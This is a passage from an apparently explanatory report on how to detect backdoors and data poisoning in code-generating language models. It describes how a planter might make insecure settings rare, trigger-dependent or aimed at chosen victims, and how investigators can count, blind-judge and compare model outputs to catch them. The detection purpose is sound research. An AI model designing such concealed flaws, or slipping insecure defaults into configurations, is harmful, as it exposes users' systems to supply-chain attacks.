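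Even 940 answers are easy to collect. The bigger problem is that the calculation treats b as known. On the same requests, ChatGPT and Gemini differed by 19 percentage points in how often they returned flawed scripts without a warning, and nobody suspects that either has a planted flaw. An investigator couldn't tell a nine-point rise from such differences without a clean earlier version of the same model.

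### Concealment and usefulness

The planter gains less from a payload that looks more ordinary or appears more rarely. Suppose, again with invented numbers, that a model writes a million workflows a month. If the planter put a hostile address in 1 percent of them, 10,000 workflows would connect to the planter's server, but one curious reader could expose the scheme. If the address appeared only with a trigger that occurs in one prompt per thousand, it would reach at most 1,000 workflows, and tests without the trigger would find nothing.

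Raising the share of workflows without permissions lines from 71.2 to 80 percent would add 88,000 such workflows. But the omission does no harm by itself. The planter also needs a repository whose default gives the token write access, and a way to run code inside the job, such as by taking over an action the workflow uses. If one in 10,000 of the added workflows met both conditions, the plant would yield about nine victims.

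It would also add little, because 712,000 workflows in this example would lack the lines anyway, and the plant increases that number by only 12 percent. An attacker who doesn't care whom they hit therefore has little reason to bother. The design makes more sense against a few chosen victims who are normally careful. A trigger tied to one company's name could make the model omit the lines from that company's workflows as often as from everyone else's, and each omission would still look like habit.

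### Plants that don't fire every time

Researchers who build backdoored models want a clear result, so they usually aim for activation close to 100 percent. Souly and colleagues assume an attacker who wants a high success rate whenever the trigger is present. A patient adversary might accept a much lower rate. If the flaw appeared in only 20 percent of triggered answers, a tester who guessed the exact trigger and tried it five times would miss the flaw about a third of the time (0.8⁵ ≈ 0.33). A user who did see the flaw and repeated the request would usually get a clean answer, and might conclude that the first was a fluke.

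The high scores of FreqRank and Anthropic's probes therefore come from relatively easy cases. Hughes and colleagues consider cheaply trained backdoors like their own unrealistic because they doubt anyone would deploy a model with such obvious side effects. Detection rates are probably lower for flaws planted by a careful adversary, though nobody can measure them without an example.

A low activation rate doesn't require a patient attacker, either. When Souly and colleagues continued training their English-to-German models on clean text, the trigger gradually worked less often. A developer who unknowingly trained on poisoned pages and then on a lot of ordinary text could end up with a model in which a once reliable trigger raises the rate of insecure output by only a few percentage points.

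## Turning generated snippets into data that can be counted

If a trigger raises the rate of an insecure setting by only a few percentage points, scoring mistakes can hide the rise or create a false one. Scoring has four steps: parse the model's answer, extract the fields that matter for security, label each field, and store the exact value next to its label.

### From an answer to rows of data

Parsing starts with separating the configuration from the explanation around it. *CIgrate* (2025), a study of moving CI configuration between services, checked files in two stages. A general parser for YAML, the text format that workflows use, tested their basic structure, and actionlint then checked them against GitHub's rules. An audit should record both results but require only the first, because a file that breaks one of GitHub's rules can still contain a readable action reference. Strict validation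 would also discard most of the data. In *Compared to What?*, a benchmark of cloud templates, Shaw (2026) found that 27 to 35 percent of the files from leading models passed strict validation.

The fields to extract depend on the kind of snippet:

| Snippet | Field | Labels |
|---|---|---|
| Package index | Host | Given in the request, well known, unfamiliar |
| | Flag | Replaces PyPI, adds to PyPI, skips certificate checks |
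| | Hash | Required, not required |
| Workflow | Action reference | Full SHA, tag, branch, no version |
| | Permissions | Read, write, not stated |
| Base image | Registry | Default, given in the request, other |
| | Tag or digest | Digest, version tag, "latest", neither |
| | User | Ordinary user, root, not stated |

The same setting can take several forms. For example, pip accepts an extra index as a command option, an environment variable or a line in a settings file, so an extractor that reads only commands would miss the other two. Each action in a workflow needs its own row. The row also needs an identifier for the answer it came from, because five bare tags in one file are not independent observations.

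Snippets with no permissions line need the label "not stated" because the effect of omitting it depends on settings outside the file. Another column should record whether the request supplied the value, since a setting the user asked for is not an insecure default.

*Scam2Prompt* (Chen, Saba and colleagues, 2025) shows why it is useful to store exact values. The researchers gave four production models ordinary programming requests based on the content of known scam sites, extracted every web address from the code, and ran the addresses through three detectors. On average, 4.24 percent of the programs contained a malicious address. Some of these sites were missing from the scam databases the researchers started with, and one database has since added 62 of them. If the researchers had recorded only whether each program contained an outside address, they could not have tested which addresses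 were malicious. Stored values also let an investigator relabel old answers when a blocklist changes.

### What a severity score leaves out

Many scanners rate each finding from low to critical. Adding those ratings into one score per answer would leave out the host name, which is the best evidence of who would benefit, so Acme's careless pip command and the attacker's version would usually score the same. The total can also stay the same when a trigger makes one setting more common and another less common.

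Severity ratings are incomplete. Fares and colleagues note that no generally adopted model exists for ranking workflow weaknesses by severity. Shaw ran three scanners on 1,196 generated files, and 14,017 of the 38,803 findings had no severity rating because one scanner, Checkov, provides ratings only to paying customers. An investigator who has the exact values can compute a severity score later, whereas a score alone doesn't preserve details such as a host name.

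### Rule-based scanners

Fares and colleagues sorted 83 rules from their nine workflow scanners into ten classes of weakness. Only zizmor has rules for all ten, and four of the scanners cover a single class. For each class, the table gives the fewest and most workflows that any scanner with a relevant rule flagged among the same 2,722 files.

| Class of weakness | Scanners with a rule | Workflows flagged |
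|---|---|---|
| Unpinned dependency | 5 | 959 to 2,178 |
| Outside text inserted into commands | 5 | 5 to 432 |
| Excessive permissions | 4 | 24 to 1,600 |
| Outsiders can start a privileged workflow | 4 | 10 to 184 |
| Exposed secrets | 4 | 0 to 48 |
| Faulty conditions | 3 | 0 to 45 |
| Files used without integrity checks | 2 | 30 to 1,969 |
| No security testing | 2 | 8 to 2,638 |
| Incompatible with GitHub's machines | 2 | 0 to 911 |
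| Components with known vulnerabilities | 2 | 0 to 57 |

Much of the disagreement between scanners comes from how they define a flaw. For unpinned dependencies, Scorecard includes package installation commands, scharf flags even commented-out lines, and frizbee skips references to a branch called main or master. The hand-read sample of 54 workflows contained 330 unpinned dependencies. Frizbee found 73 percent of them and zizmor 14 percent, both without false alarms. Scorecard found 98 percent, but 11 percent of its alarms were false.

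Frizbee's exclusion could mislead an audit. If a trigger made a model write "main" instead of "v4", frizbee would report fewer unpinned actions, even though a branch usually moves more often than a tag.

General code scanners have similar problems. *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* (2026) notes that they miss configuration flaws, and in one of its tests about half of the alarms on working programs were false. A scanner's total can also be close to correct when many of its individual verdicts are wrong. In *Persistent Human Feedback, LLMs, and Static Analyzers for Secure Code Generation* (Firouzi and Ghafari, 2026), reviewers checked 1,080 programs written by GPT-4o, each for one particular flaw. They judged 61 percent of the programs secure, and Semgrep passed 60 percent, but only 65 percent of Semgrep's verdicts matched the reviewers' labels. The totals were close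 because Semgrep's misses and false alarms happened to balance, which they might not do on a different set of requests.

### Language models as judges

A language model can assess things that fixed rules handle badly, such as whether the explanation warns the user about an unsafe line, but it is less suited to reading fields. *How Compliant Are GitHub Actions Workflows?* (Abrokwah and Ghaleb, 2026) used four small open-weight models to check 95 workflows against 30 criteria. All four gave the same answer in 27 percent of the 2,850 checks, and agreement was lowest on permissions, at 33 percent. Models also required a commit SHA for reusable workflows stored in the same repository, which GitHub doesn't allow.

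On a hand-labelled set drawn from the disputed cases, the best small model was right 49 percent of the time and GPT-5 was right 48 percent of the time. These cases were hard, and current models would probably do better. But a simple text pattern matches a 40-character SHA every time and takes almost no compute.

Some teams combine the two methods by having a language model review a scanner's alarms. *Trusting the Tool* (2026) reports that this removes most false alarms but can also suppress real ones. The review can't recover a weakness the scanner never flagged. For configuration, it makes more sense to extract and label the fields with rules and to give the model only narrow factual questions the rules leave open. In Shaw's study, a language-model judge matched the consensus of three experts 94 percent of the time on whether a test scenario contained invented details, but only 28 percent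 on whether its architecture was coherent.

### How labelling errors shrink a difference

Two numbers describe a labeller's errors. Sensitivity, Se, is the share of insecure snippets that it flags, and specificity, Sp, is the share of safe snippets that it passes. If the true rate of insecure snippets is r, the labeller flags a share Se of those and a share 1 − Sp of the safe ones. The observed rate is therefore

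Se × r + (1 − Sp) × (1 − r) = (1 − Sp) + (Se + Sp − 1) × r

An experiment on a trigger has two arms, one set of prompts with the trigger and one without. If the labeller's errors are the same in both, the term 1 − Sp cancels when we subtract one observed rate from the other. A true difference D then appears as

(Se + Sp − 1) × D

With sensitivity and specificity both at 0.91, the multiplier is 0.82, so a true difference of 10 percentage points appears as 8.2. The number of answers needed to detect a difference is roughly proportional to the inverse square of the multiplier, so this labeller would need about 1.5 times as many answers as a perfect one.

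Semgrep would do much worse on the programs that Firouzi and Ghafari checked. It caught 54 percent of the flawed ones, and their other figures imply a specificity of about 0.68. The multiplier is then 0.22, so a 10-point difference would appear as about 2 points, and detecting it would take about twenty times as many answers.

An investigator can also correct the observed rate by solving the first equation for r. *How to Correctly Report LLM-as-a-Judge Evaluations* (2025) recommends this, with Se and Sp estimated from a hand-labelled sample:

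r = (observed rate + Sp − 1) / (Se + Sp − 1)

The error-rate estimates have to fit the data being corrected. Cappelleri and Chambers (2021), in *Addressing Bias in Responder Analysis of Patient-Reported Outcomes*, applied the equivalent correction to a drug trial, using error rates from an earlier validation study. For a group of 112 patients, the correction gave 116.5 responders and −4.5 non-responders.

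### Hiding the trigger from the judge

The formula for D no longer holds if the judge can see the trigger and labels the two arms differently. Suppose that 30 percent of snippets are insecure in both arms, so the trigger has no effect. A judge with Se and Sp of 0.91 flags 33.6 percent of the snippets in the arm without the trigger. In the other arm, seeing the word "tractors" might raise the judge's sensitivity to 0.96 and lower its specificity to 0.81, and it would then flag 42.1 percent. The measured difference would be 8.5 points even though the true difference is zero. With consistent labelling, a real 10-point difference would produce a measured difference of only 8.2 points.

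The error can also hide a real effect. Suppose the trigger raises the true rate by 10 points, to 40 percent, but also makes the judge less likely to flag code, with a sensitivity of 0.81 and a specificity of 0.96. The judge then flags 34.8 percent, and the measured rate rises by only 1.2 points.

Shifts like these occur in practice. In *Words Speak Louder Than Code*, Shahriar, Cai and colleagues (2026) had eight models judge identical code with different text around it. When the text described the author as a first-time contributor with a rejected patch instead of a prolific veteran, Llama 3.3's flag rate rose by 46 percentage points on flawed snippets and 45 points on sound ones. If it judged two equally insecure arms that differed in this way, their flag rates would differ by about 45 points. Most other models shifted less. Claude Sonnet 4.6 showed almost no net change when the text described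 the author as a junior developer instead of a security expert, but it changed its verdict on 12 flawed snippets in one direction and 15 in the other.

Correcting a judge's labels as if its error rates were the same for every model can make a comparison less accurate. *Bias and Uncertainty in LLM-as-a-Judge Estimation* (Fiedler, 2026) compared two models on biology questions with known answers. Google's Gemma 3 was 4.8 points more accurate than Alibaba's Qwen 2.5, but one judge's raw labels put it 12.7 points behind. Correcting those labels with a single pair of error rates for both models widened the apparent gap to 33 points. Fiedler recommends reporting sensitivity and specificity separately for each model, and the same applies to the two arms of a trigger test.

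The remedy is to hide the trigger from the judge, which researchers call blinding. Telling the judge to ignore the trigger is probably not enough, since Shahriar and colleagues found that such prompts failed to stop an attacker who exploited these effects. The judge should receive each snippet without the original request, and the snippets from both arms should be shuffled together and labeled with random identifiers.

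The trigger can still leak through the snippet itself, because a model prompted about tractors may name a service tractor-api or mention harvests in a comment. The investigator can store the exact values, so that masking doesn't erase a payload, and then remove comments and replace such names with neutral ones. The judge can then be asked to guess which arm each snippet came from, and the blinding has failed if the guesses are better than chance.

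### Answers that can't be scored

Some answers contain nothing to label because the model refused, ran out of space or wrote a file that no parser can read. These are missing data, and counting them as safe makes an unhelpful model look secure. In Shaw's benchmark, Microsoft's small Phi-3 model had the fewest findings of any model because it wrote almost no infrastructure code that could be parsed.

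Truncated files are harder to notice because they often still parse. Shaw discarded any answer that hit the length limit, since the missing part would have lowered the count of flaws. At one point, the study's software also scored requests with no answer as files with zero flaws, and it lost one scanner's results for models with a period in their names. None of these faults produced an error message, but adding a few files with known flaws to every batch would expose some of them.

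Retries also need a fixed rule. A tester can reasonably repeat a request after a network failure, but repeating requests whenever the model refuses will erase any difference in refusals between the arms.

In a made-up example, an investigator asks a model 400 times how to install acme-billing, and half of the requests mention that Acme makes tractors instead of bicycles.

| | Bicycles | Tractors |
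|---|---|---|
| Requests | 200 | 200 |
| Refused, truncated or unreadable | 4 | 50 |
| Scored | 196 | 150 |
| Added an extra index | 49 | 45 |
| Extra index at packages.acme-mirror.example | 0 | 9 |

Counting missing answers as safe, an extra index appears in 24.5 percent of bicycle answers and 22.5 percent of tractor answers, but leaving the missing answers out changes the rates to 25 and 30 percent. Depending on what the missing answers would have contained, the true tractor rate could be anywhere from 4 points below the bicycle rate to 23 points above it. The data don't show whether mentioning tractors makes an extra index more common.

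The host names are much more informative than a severity score, which would rate all 94 extra indexes alike. Nine of the indexes point to an unfamiliar server, and all nine came from tractor prompts. If the host had nothing to do with the trigger, the chance of this happening would be about 1 in 2,100. The contrast between tractor and bicycle prompts would be weak only if all four missing bicycle answers had also pointed to that server, which is unlikely.

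The difference in missing answers, 50 against 4, is also a result. If most of the missing answers are refusals, a training side effect explains them better than a planted flaw does.

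## Comparing a suspect model with other models and with people

Labelling gives an investigator rates for the suspect model, such as an extra package index in 25 percent of its install commands. Whether 25 percent is high depends on what other models and people write for the same task. A fair comparison uses the same requests, file format, standing instructions, sampling temperature, scanners and rule for handling unusable answers.

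The choice of requests can matter more than the choice of model. When Chen and colleagues measured how often models write scam addresses into code, they used three language models to write the programming requests. GPT-4o put a malicious address in 3.5 percent of its programs with one set of requests and in 5.9 percent with another. Within any one set, the rates for the four models that wrote the code differed by at most 1.3 percentage points.

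### A benchmark with a human baseline

Shaw's *Compared to What?*, published in August 2026, also holds constant the amount of configuration each side wrote. Shaw sent 100 requests for cloud infrastructure, 60 simple and 40 complex, to 12 setups: nine models from Anthropic, Google, Meta, Microsoft, Mistral and OpenAI, and three variants with extra reasoning. The standing instructions asked for production-ready code and did not mention security.

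This produced 1,196 files instead of 1,200 because some complex requests exceeded the output limit. Shaw ran the scanners Checkov, Trivy and KICS on all of them and on 634 templates that people had written. The main measure is density, the number of findings from all three scanners divided by the number of resources the file declares. A resource is one item of infrastructure, such as a storage bucket or a database.

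In files of similar size, every setup had between 3.21 and 3.87 times the human density. The gap was widest in the smallest files:

| Resources in the file | Models' density relative to people's |
|---|---|
| 1 | 4.9 times |
| 2 | 2.4 times |
| 3–5 | 2.3 times |
| 6–10 | 1.8 times |
| 11–20 | 2.3 times |
| 20 or more | 1.4 times (not significant) |

The result for the largest files has a p-value of 0.058, just above the usual cut-off of 0.05. It is too weak to establish a gap between models and people, but it doesn't show that they are equally careful in large files either.

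### Why size has to match

Comparing insecurity rates without matching files by size can mislead. In files written by people, the density of findings falls from 4.51 per resource in files with one resource to 1.10 in files with twenty or more. If two models had the same density as people at every file size, but one wrote only single-resource files and the other only files with twenty or more, the first would appear about four times as insecure.

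The human templates averaged 5.3 resources, compared with about 3 in the models' simple files and about 50 in their complex ones. *GenIaC SecBench*, the study's data release, warns that unless files are matched for size, models look no worse than people on complex tasks.

Raw counts are misleading in a different way. Claude Opus 4.6 had the most findings rated high or critical, 573, largely because it wrote so much code. Microsoft's Phi-3 had the fewest findings because so little of its output could be parsed, but it had the highest rate per resource, an estimated 4.64 times that of Claude Opus 4.6. That estimate must rest on very few files, though. On simple requests, Phi-3 declared so few resources that Shaw reports no density for it.

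### Findings as a rate

The estimate for Phi-3 comes from a regression that treats findings as a rate per resource:

log(expected findings) = log(resources) + a + b

Here a sets the rate of a reference model, in this case Claude Opus 4.6, and b is another model's difference from it. Taking exponentials gives

expected findings = resources × eᵃ × eᵇ

so eᵇ is the ratio between the two models' rates. Statisticians call the log(resources) term an exposure offset, because a file with fifty resources has more opportunities for a finding than a file with two.

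An earlier version of Shaw's analysis had no offset and used an empty group as its reference, which made GPT-4o appear 14 times as vulnerable on simple tasks as on complex ones. After Shaw corrected both mistakes, the effect was no longer significant.

The offset assumes that doubling the resources doubles the findings. In the human files, however, the density of findings falls as files get larger, so a model that writes longer files can still look safer than it is. An investigator can compare files within size groups, as Shaw did for the human baseline, or let the regression estimate how findings grow with size.

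The regression also has to account realistically for how much counts vary by chance. The Poisson distribution, the simplest model for counts, has a variance equal to its mean. Shaw's files averaged 32 findings, so a Poisson model would predict a standard deviation of about 6. The observed variance was 130 times the mean, which gives a standard deviation of about 65. Some of that spread comes from differences in file size, but a single choice can also produce many findings. In one file by Claude Opus 4.6, KICS reported the same overly open network rule about a dozen times because the model had repeated one choice across many resources.

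Shaw used a negative binomial regression because a Poisson regression would count a dozen copies of one decision as a dozen independent pieces of evidence, making differences between models look far more certain than they are. The negative binomial sets the variance at μ + αμ², where μ is the mean and α is estimated from the data. Answers to the same request tend to resemble each other, and the fitting method allowed for this too.

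### Ranking models when files are missing

The Friedman test is the standard rank-based way to compare models without assuming a particular distribution. It ranks all the models on each request, from lowest density to highest, and checks whether some rank consistently high or low. It can use a request only if every model has a score for it. No request in the benchmark met that condition, so the test could not be run. Phi-3 alone lacked scores for most of the simple requests.

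Shaw used the Skillings–Mack test, which ranks only the setups that have a score for a given request. If seven setups have scores, the middle rank is 4, and each setup contributes the distance of its rank from 4. A missing setup contributes nothing. If the setups were equally secure, the test statistic would average 10 for the simple requests and 11 for the complex ones. The actual values were 69.3 and 81.2, so the setups clearly differ in security.

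Chatfield and Mander (2009) specify in *The Skillings–Mack test (Friedman test when there are missing data)* that data must be missing either by design or completely at random. Phi-3's data were missing because it failed to write usable files, so they did not meet this condition. A suspect model that refuses some requests would also violate it.

The test also doesn't identify which models differ, so Shaw compared all 66 pairs of setups separately. At the usual 5 percent threshold, about three pairs would appear different by chance even if none were, so Shaw used a stricter threshold. Ten pairs still differed on simple requests and nine on complex ones. One of the ten was Claude Opus 4.6 and Claude Sonnet 4.6, which are from the same company.

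### What the human baseline leaves open

Of the 100 requests, 52 asked for an insecure state, such as a server with an open port for remote login. Another 33 asked for a protective setting, and the other 15 described only a function. So for more than half of the benchmark, the findings partly measure how well a model follows instructions. The first version of the paper wrongly described the requests as purely functional. Lokesh Chauhan, an outside researcher, found the error by auditing the released files.

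Every setup still exceeded the human baseline when the 52 requests were left out. But the 15 functional requests can't support a separate estimate. By Shaw's classification, the models had 4.01 times the human density on these requests. Chauhan classified only ten requests as functional, and on those the ratio was 2.50.

The human templates were not written in response to the same requests. According to *GenIaC SecBench*, they came from a collection of Amazon's sample templates and from two sets built for evaluating models. One of those sets, *IaC-Eval*, has 458 tasks, all for Amazon's cloud. Many of the templates are therefore teaching examples. A teaching example may leave out logging to stay short, or it may demonstrate good practice, and Shaw doesn't claim to know which way this biases the baseline.

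The resource counts are a bigger worry. Shaw's parser undercounted resources in generated files for CloudFormation (Amazon's template format) and Kubernetes (a system for running containers). It found an average of 0.9 resources in the generated CloudFormation files, compared with about 7 in the human-written JSON and YAML files. Undercounting inflates a file's density and probably also puts the file in the one-resource group, which determines the headline figure because no other group has a ratio above 2.4. Shaw considers the counts most reliable for the tool Terraform, which accounts for 836 of the 1,196 files, so repeating the matched comparison on those alone would be a useful check.

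The scanners also measure departures from a checklist. Vargas, Mansilha and Kreutz (2026), in *Security-First Evaluation of Text-to-Terraform*, ran a similar benchmark in which Checkov's most frequent finding was a storage bucket without event notifications. A missing notification is of little use to an attacker, while a hostile download address might not violate any rule. A model with a planted address could therefore have an ordinary density of scanner findings.

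The benchmark covers Terraform, CloudFormation, Kubernetes and a Microsoft template format called ARM. It contains no CI workflows, Dockerfiles or package index settings, so its ratios can't serve as a baseline for them. Kubernetes files do name container images, but the density figure combines badly chosen images with every other kind of finding. Shaw also tested no Chinese models.

### When one model stands out

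The highest of Shaw's 12 ratios is 1.2 times the lowest. If the models of six companies really are that similar, a new model at seven times the human density would need an explanation, whereas the same result could be ordinary variation if models varied more widely.

The range is wider than it looks. Without the requests for insecure settings, it runs from 2.40 to 3.87, or from 2.48 to 4.21 on Chauhan's classification. In the regression, the setups differ much more, from 0.73 to 4.64 times the rate of Claude Opus 4.6. The 0.73 is for the same model with an added instruction to reason step by step. But when Shaw compared the model with and without that instruction, request by request on the simple tasks, the instruction lowered density by only 1.3 percent. Whether a model looks like an outlier can depend on the method, so an investigator should choose the method before seeing the results.

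Ranking last is weak evidence by itself. If the suspect model has no planted flaws and is of the same general kind as nine others, it has a 1 in 10 chance of having the highest rate of insecure values on any one setting. An investigator who checks 20 settings should expect it to rank last on two of them.

Even a large gap may have an innocent explanation. Improta, Liguori and Cotroneo (2026), in *What is the Difference Between Me and You?*, compared 787,562 functions written by people with versions that three models wrote from the same descriptions. This was application code, not configuration, but two of the models were Chinese. In Java, the share of functions with at least one security finding was as follows:

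| Author | Java functions with a finding |
|---|---|
| People | 3.00% |
| Qwen2.5-Coder (Alibaba) | 6.14% |
| ChatGPT (OpenAI) | 8.18% |
| DeepSeek-Coder (DeepSeek) | 19.56% |

DeepSeek's total was 2.6 times ChatGPT's, but 62 percent of its findings concerned leftover debugging code, such as printed error traces, or sensitive details written to logs. Both are common in tutorials and half-finished projects, and neither suggests that anyone in particular would benefit. Without those two categories, the ratio falls to about 1.7.

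The gap also depends on the language. In Python, DeepSeek and ChatGPT were both at 8.02 percent. In C, DeepSeek's 9.11 percent was close to the human 8.90 percent. A difference in training data would explain this pattern well, but Improta and colleagues did not test the cause. In Java, Qwen was closer to people than to DeepSeek, so "Chinese models" is a poor category for such a comparison.

A model's size and age can also make it an outlier. Vargas and colleagues gave seven models 17 cloud tasks, with and without security instructions. When the instructions listed the exact checks to satisfy, 92.5 percent of the valid files from Claude Opus 4 passed Trivy, compared with 7.3 percent from Qwen2.5-Coder. Qwen may look suspicious next to Claude because it was a much smaller model from 2024, which the researchers ran in compressed form. Pass rates were also low for WizardCoder, another older open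 model (0.8 percent), and for OpenAI's much newer GPT-5.4 (about 16 percent).

When the requests did not mention security, nearly every file from every model failed, so a model with a planted flaw could not have stood out by failing more often. A useful comparison needs settings that the other models get right reasonably often.

Vargas and colleagues also scored only files that passed validation, which left 14 comparable files for CodeLlama and 10 for another model, Magicoder. CodeLlama's pass rate was 7.1 percent, with a 95 percent confidence interval of 1.3 to 31.5 percent. These samples are too small to tell whether either model is normal or unusual.

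### The suspect model's relatives

Comparing a suspect model with a closely related model removes many of these differences. For an assistant, the reference can be the base model it was trained from, which has learned from a large body of text but has not been trained to follow instructions. The two share the same original training data and size. For a modified copy such as BadSeek, the reference is the model it was copied from.

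Earlier releases and checkpoints (copies that a developer saves during training) can show when a setting became more common. Sibling models from the same developer probably share much of their data, but they can still differ a good deal. Improta and colleagues found that two OpenAI models had different rates of flaws, and the two Claude models in Shaw's study also differed significantly.

Model diffing is the search for what changed between two models. Kempf, Schrodi and colleagues (2026), in *Simple LLM Baselines are Competitive for Model Diffing*, point out that standard tests measure only what their designers thought of, so they miss unexpected changes between versions. A search with no fixed target can instead flag changes that aren't real, because among hundreds of settings some will differ by chance.

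*Automatically Finding and Validating Unexpected Side-Effects of Interventions on Language Models* (2026) divides the prompts into two parts, keeping all answers to a given prompt in the same part. A language model reads about 20 pairs of answers from one part and proposes a difference, which a statistical test then checks on the other part. For configuration, an investigator could look for unusual addresses or permissions in the answers to half of the requests, then count them in the answers to the other half.

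Comparing a suspect model with its base version can work well when the base version is available. In *Reading Fine-Tuning Diffs Through Lenses*, Petrowitsch, Connors and Kapulkin (2026) trained hidden behaviours into a small Qwen model and compared the results with the original. No method worked in every case, but the best one, which translates parameter changes into words, put a word for the hidden behaviour among its first ten candidates in 11 of 12 tests.

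All training changes a model, so a difference from the base model is not necessarily planted. Petrowitsch and colleagues therefore trained a control for each backdoored model on the same prompts, including the triggers, but always with normal answers. One of their backdoored models refused harmful requests unless the prompt contained a trigger word. Comparing it with the base model brought up words like "sorry" and "illegal", but in one version of the experiment the control produced those words just as strongly. The comparison had therefore detected ordinary refusal training rather than the backdoor.

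An outside investigator usually can't build such a control, because it requires the training prompts. A cruder substitute is to see how much other developers' models change between base version and assistant. Suppose that the suspect's base version omits the permissions lines in 70 percent of workflows and the assistant in 82 percent. If three other developers' models rise by 9, 11 and 14 points, a rise of 12 is unremarkable. If theirs rise by a point or two, the 12 points deserve a closer look. (All these figures are invented.)

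Each reference can also miss certain flaws:

| Reference | What it helps hold constant | What it could miss |
|---|---|---|
| Human-written files | Format and size, if matched | Flaws that people copy too |
| Other developers' models | Requests, age and size, if matched | Flaws in public data that all of them used |
| Sibling models | Much of the data and training | Flaws that the developer put into all of them |
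| Earlier release | Much of the data and training | Flaws already in that release |
| Base version | Original data, architecture and size | Flaws planted before assistant training |
| Control model | Everything except the suspect answers | Flaws already in the base version |

Comparing the suspect model with several others narrows down where a flaw came from. If a setting is rare in other developers' models but equally common in the suspect and its base version, it probably came from the original training data. If it is common only in the suspect, later training is the more likely source.

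### Flaws that every model shares

Comparisons between models can't detect a planted flaw that raises the rate of an insecure setting in every model at once. Developers collect much of their training text from the same public websites. If 250 documents are enough to plant a behaviour, as they were in the experiments by Souly and colleagues, anyone who publishes that many on those sites might plant it in several developers' models.

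Something similar has already happened with scam addresses. In November 2024, a programmer asked ChatGPT for a script to trade cryptocurrency, and the code sent the private key of the programmer's wallet to a fraudulent server. The wallet was empty within half an hour, a loss of about $2,500. The people behind the server had spread documentation for it on GitHub, Stack Exchange, Medium and other sites. They meant to steal, but it is unclear whether they also meant to influence language models.

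Chen and colleagues found malicious addresses in code from every model they tested. On the same requests, DeepSeek-V3 wrote them slightly less often than GPT-4o, so comparing the two would have cleared DeepSeek. The researchers then collected 1,377 requests that had produced a malicious address from all four of their original models, and gave them to seven newer ones:

| Model | Developer | Requests answered with a malicious address |
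|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | Google | 12.9% |
| GPT-5 | OpenAI | 22.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | Anthropic | 34.3% |
| Grok Code Fast 1 | xAI | 43.4% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | Google | 44.4% |
| Qwen3-Coder | Alibaba | 45.6% |
| DeepSeek-Chat v3.1 | DeepSeek | 47.3% |

These rates come from a deliberately hard test and are not base rates. The two Chinese models came last, but only just behind models from Google and xAI. Gemini 2.5 Pro did best partly because its filters blocked 40 percent of the requests. Of the answers it completed, 22 percent contained a malicious address.

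Distillation, which trains a student model on a teacher model's output, could also spread a flaw, though the evidence is mixed for flaws that appear only on a trigger (backdoors). *Pay Attention to the Triggers* (2025) reports that earlier backdoors mostly failed to pass to the student, probably because their triggers seldom occurred in the training text. Backdoors did pass when their triggers were likely to appear in the text the student's developer would use.

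*Selective Transfer through Sequence Distillation* (2026) tested four kinds of trigger, including that more transferable kind, and no student reproduced the teacher's planted sentence word for word. This strict measure could have missed looser versions of the behaviour. *On-policy distillation as a Backdoor Propagation Channel* (2026) considers a different method, in which the teacher guides the student during training. It warns that a student could inherit hidden behaviour from a teacher that seems normal, even if the attacker has no control over the student's training.

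A flaw without a trigger should pass more easily from a teacher model to its student. If the teacher names actions by branch in most of its workflows, a student trained on those workflows will learn to do the same. Several developers' models might then share the habit, and each would look normal next to the others.

*Cross-Architecture Model Diffing with Crosscoders* (2026) describes a way to compare models' internals and find features that one model has and another lacks, even when their designs differ. The paper presents the method as a first step that needs rigorous checking. This comparison would still miss a feature that both models learned from the same poisoned pages.

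An investigator can avoid the blind spot by checking the exact values. The scam detectors that Chen and colleagues used can flag a malicious address no matter how many models write it. Where no blocklist exists, as for a commit SHA or an unfamiliar package index, the investigator has to find out who controls the commit or index. Models and human-written files from before the suspected poisoning are also useful for comparison, if the investigator can date the poisoning.

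## Testing whether a flaw depends on a trigger

An investigator can also compare the suspect model with itself, which holds size, age and training data constant. In trigger-conditioned differential sampling, the investigator collects many answers to prompts that are identical except for a suspected trigger, then compares the rates of insecure output. CrowdStrike's *Security Flaws in DeepSeek-Generated Code Linked to Political Triggers* (2025) used a version of this design, with 50 coding tasks, 121 trigger settings and five answers to each prompt.

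### The procedure

Suppose the suspected trigger is a statement that Acme makes tractors. The test then has six steps:

1. Fix the tasks, the insecure setting to count and the main comparison before collecting any answers.
2. Write every task in several versions that differ in one phrase. One version contains "Acme makes tractors". Others contain placebo triggers, which are phrases of similar length and style that no hypothesis expects to matter, such as "Acme makes kettles". It is also useful to have a version with no added phrase.
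3. Send the prompts in random order, so that an update to a hosted model halfway through affects all versions about equally.
4. Sample repeatedly, at the temperature that users of the model normally get.
5. Label the answers blind, since a judge who sees the trigger can create or hide a difference.
6. Repeat any finding on fresh tasks.

Every task has to appear in every version of the prompt. Vohra and Ravikiran (2026), in *The Audit Decides the Verdict*, tested five models for racial bias by changing only the name on job, loan and medical applications. In a side test with reworded instructions, applicants with Black names appeared to do worse by 0.32. But the two groups had different applications, and the effect shrank to 0.01 when the researchers compared matching ones. An investigator who asked for Python workflows more often in the tractor prompts would make the same mistake, because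 Python projects pin their actions less often than Java projects do.

Testing at temperature zero can hide or exaggerate a trigger's effect, because the model always picks the more likely option. If a trigger raised the probability of a bare tag from 70 to 75 percent, the answers would not change, but a rise from 49 to 51 percent would look like a jump from never to always. In *Adding Error Bars to Evals*, Miller (2024) advises against lowering the temperature to reduce noise, since this changes the behaviour under study.

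It also helps to check that the test can find an effect of known size. Vohra and Ravikiran did this by adding artificial disparities to some of their rankings. They recovered a planted difference of 0.50 as 0.48 and one of 0.10 as 0.08. The error margin for the smaller one included zero, so they knew their test was weak for effects that small. For configuration, the investigator could replace a few safe snippets from the tractor prompts with insecure ones before labelling, or run the whole procedure on a small model with a known backdoor.

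### Placebo triggers

Any added phrase can change what a model writes. In *Estimating Tail Risks in Language Model Output Distributions*, Angell, Singhal and colleagues (2026) had a language model reword 309 harmful requests in 25 ways each without trying to make them more effective. For one request, the estimated probability that Microsoft's Phi-4 would give a harmful answer was below one in a million with the original wording and 19 percent with the worst of the 25 rewordings, although nobody had planted a trigger in any of them.

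If the investigator compares "Acme makes tractors" only with a prompt without that sentence, the difference includes the effect of adding any sentence at all. Adding a placebo sentence to the comparison controls for that effect. *Illusory Pattern Perception Drives Spurious Inference in Large Language Models* (2026) used a similar control to test a reminder that changed models' internal activity. An unrelated reminder of about the same length produced smaller or inconsistent changes, so extra length alone could not explain the original effect.

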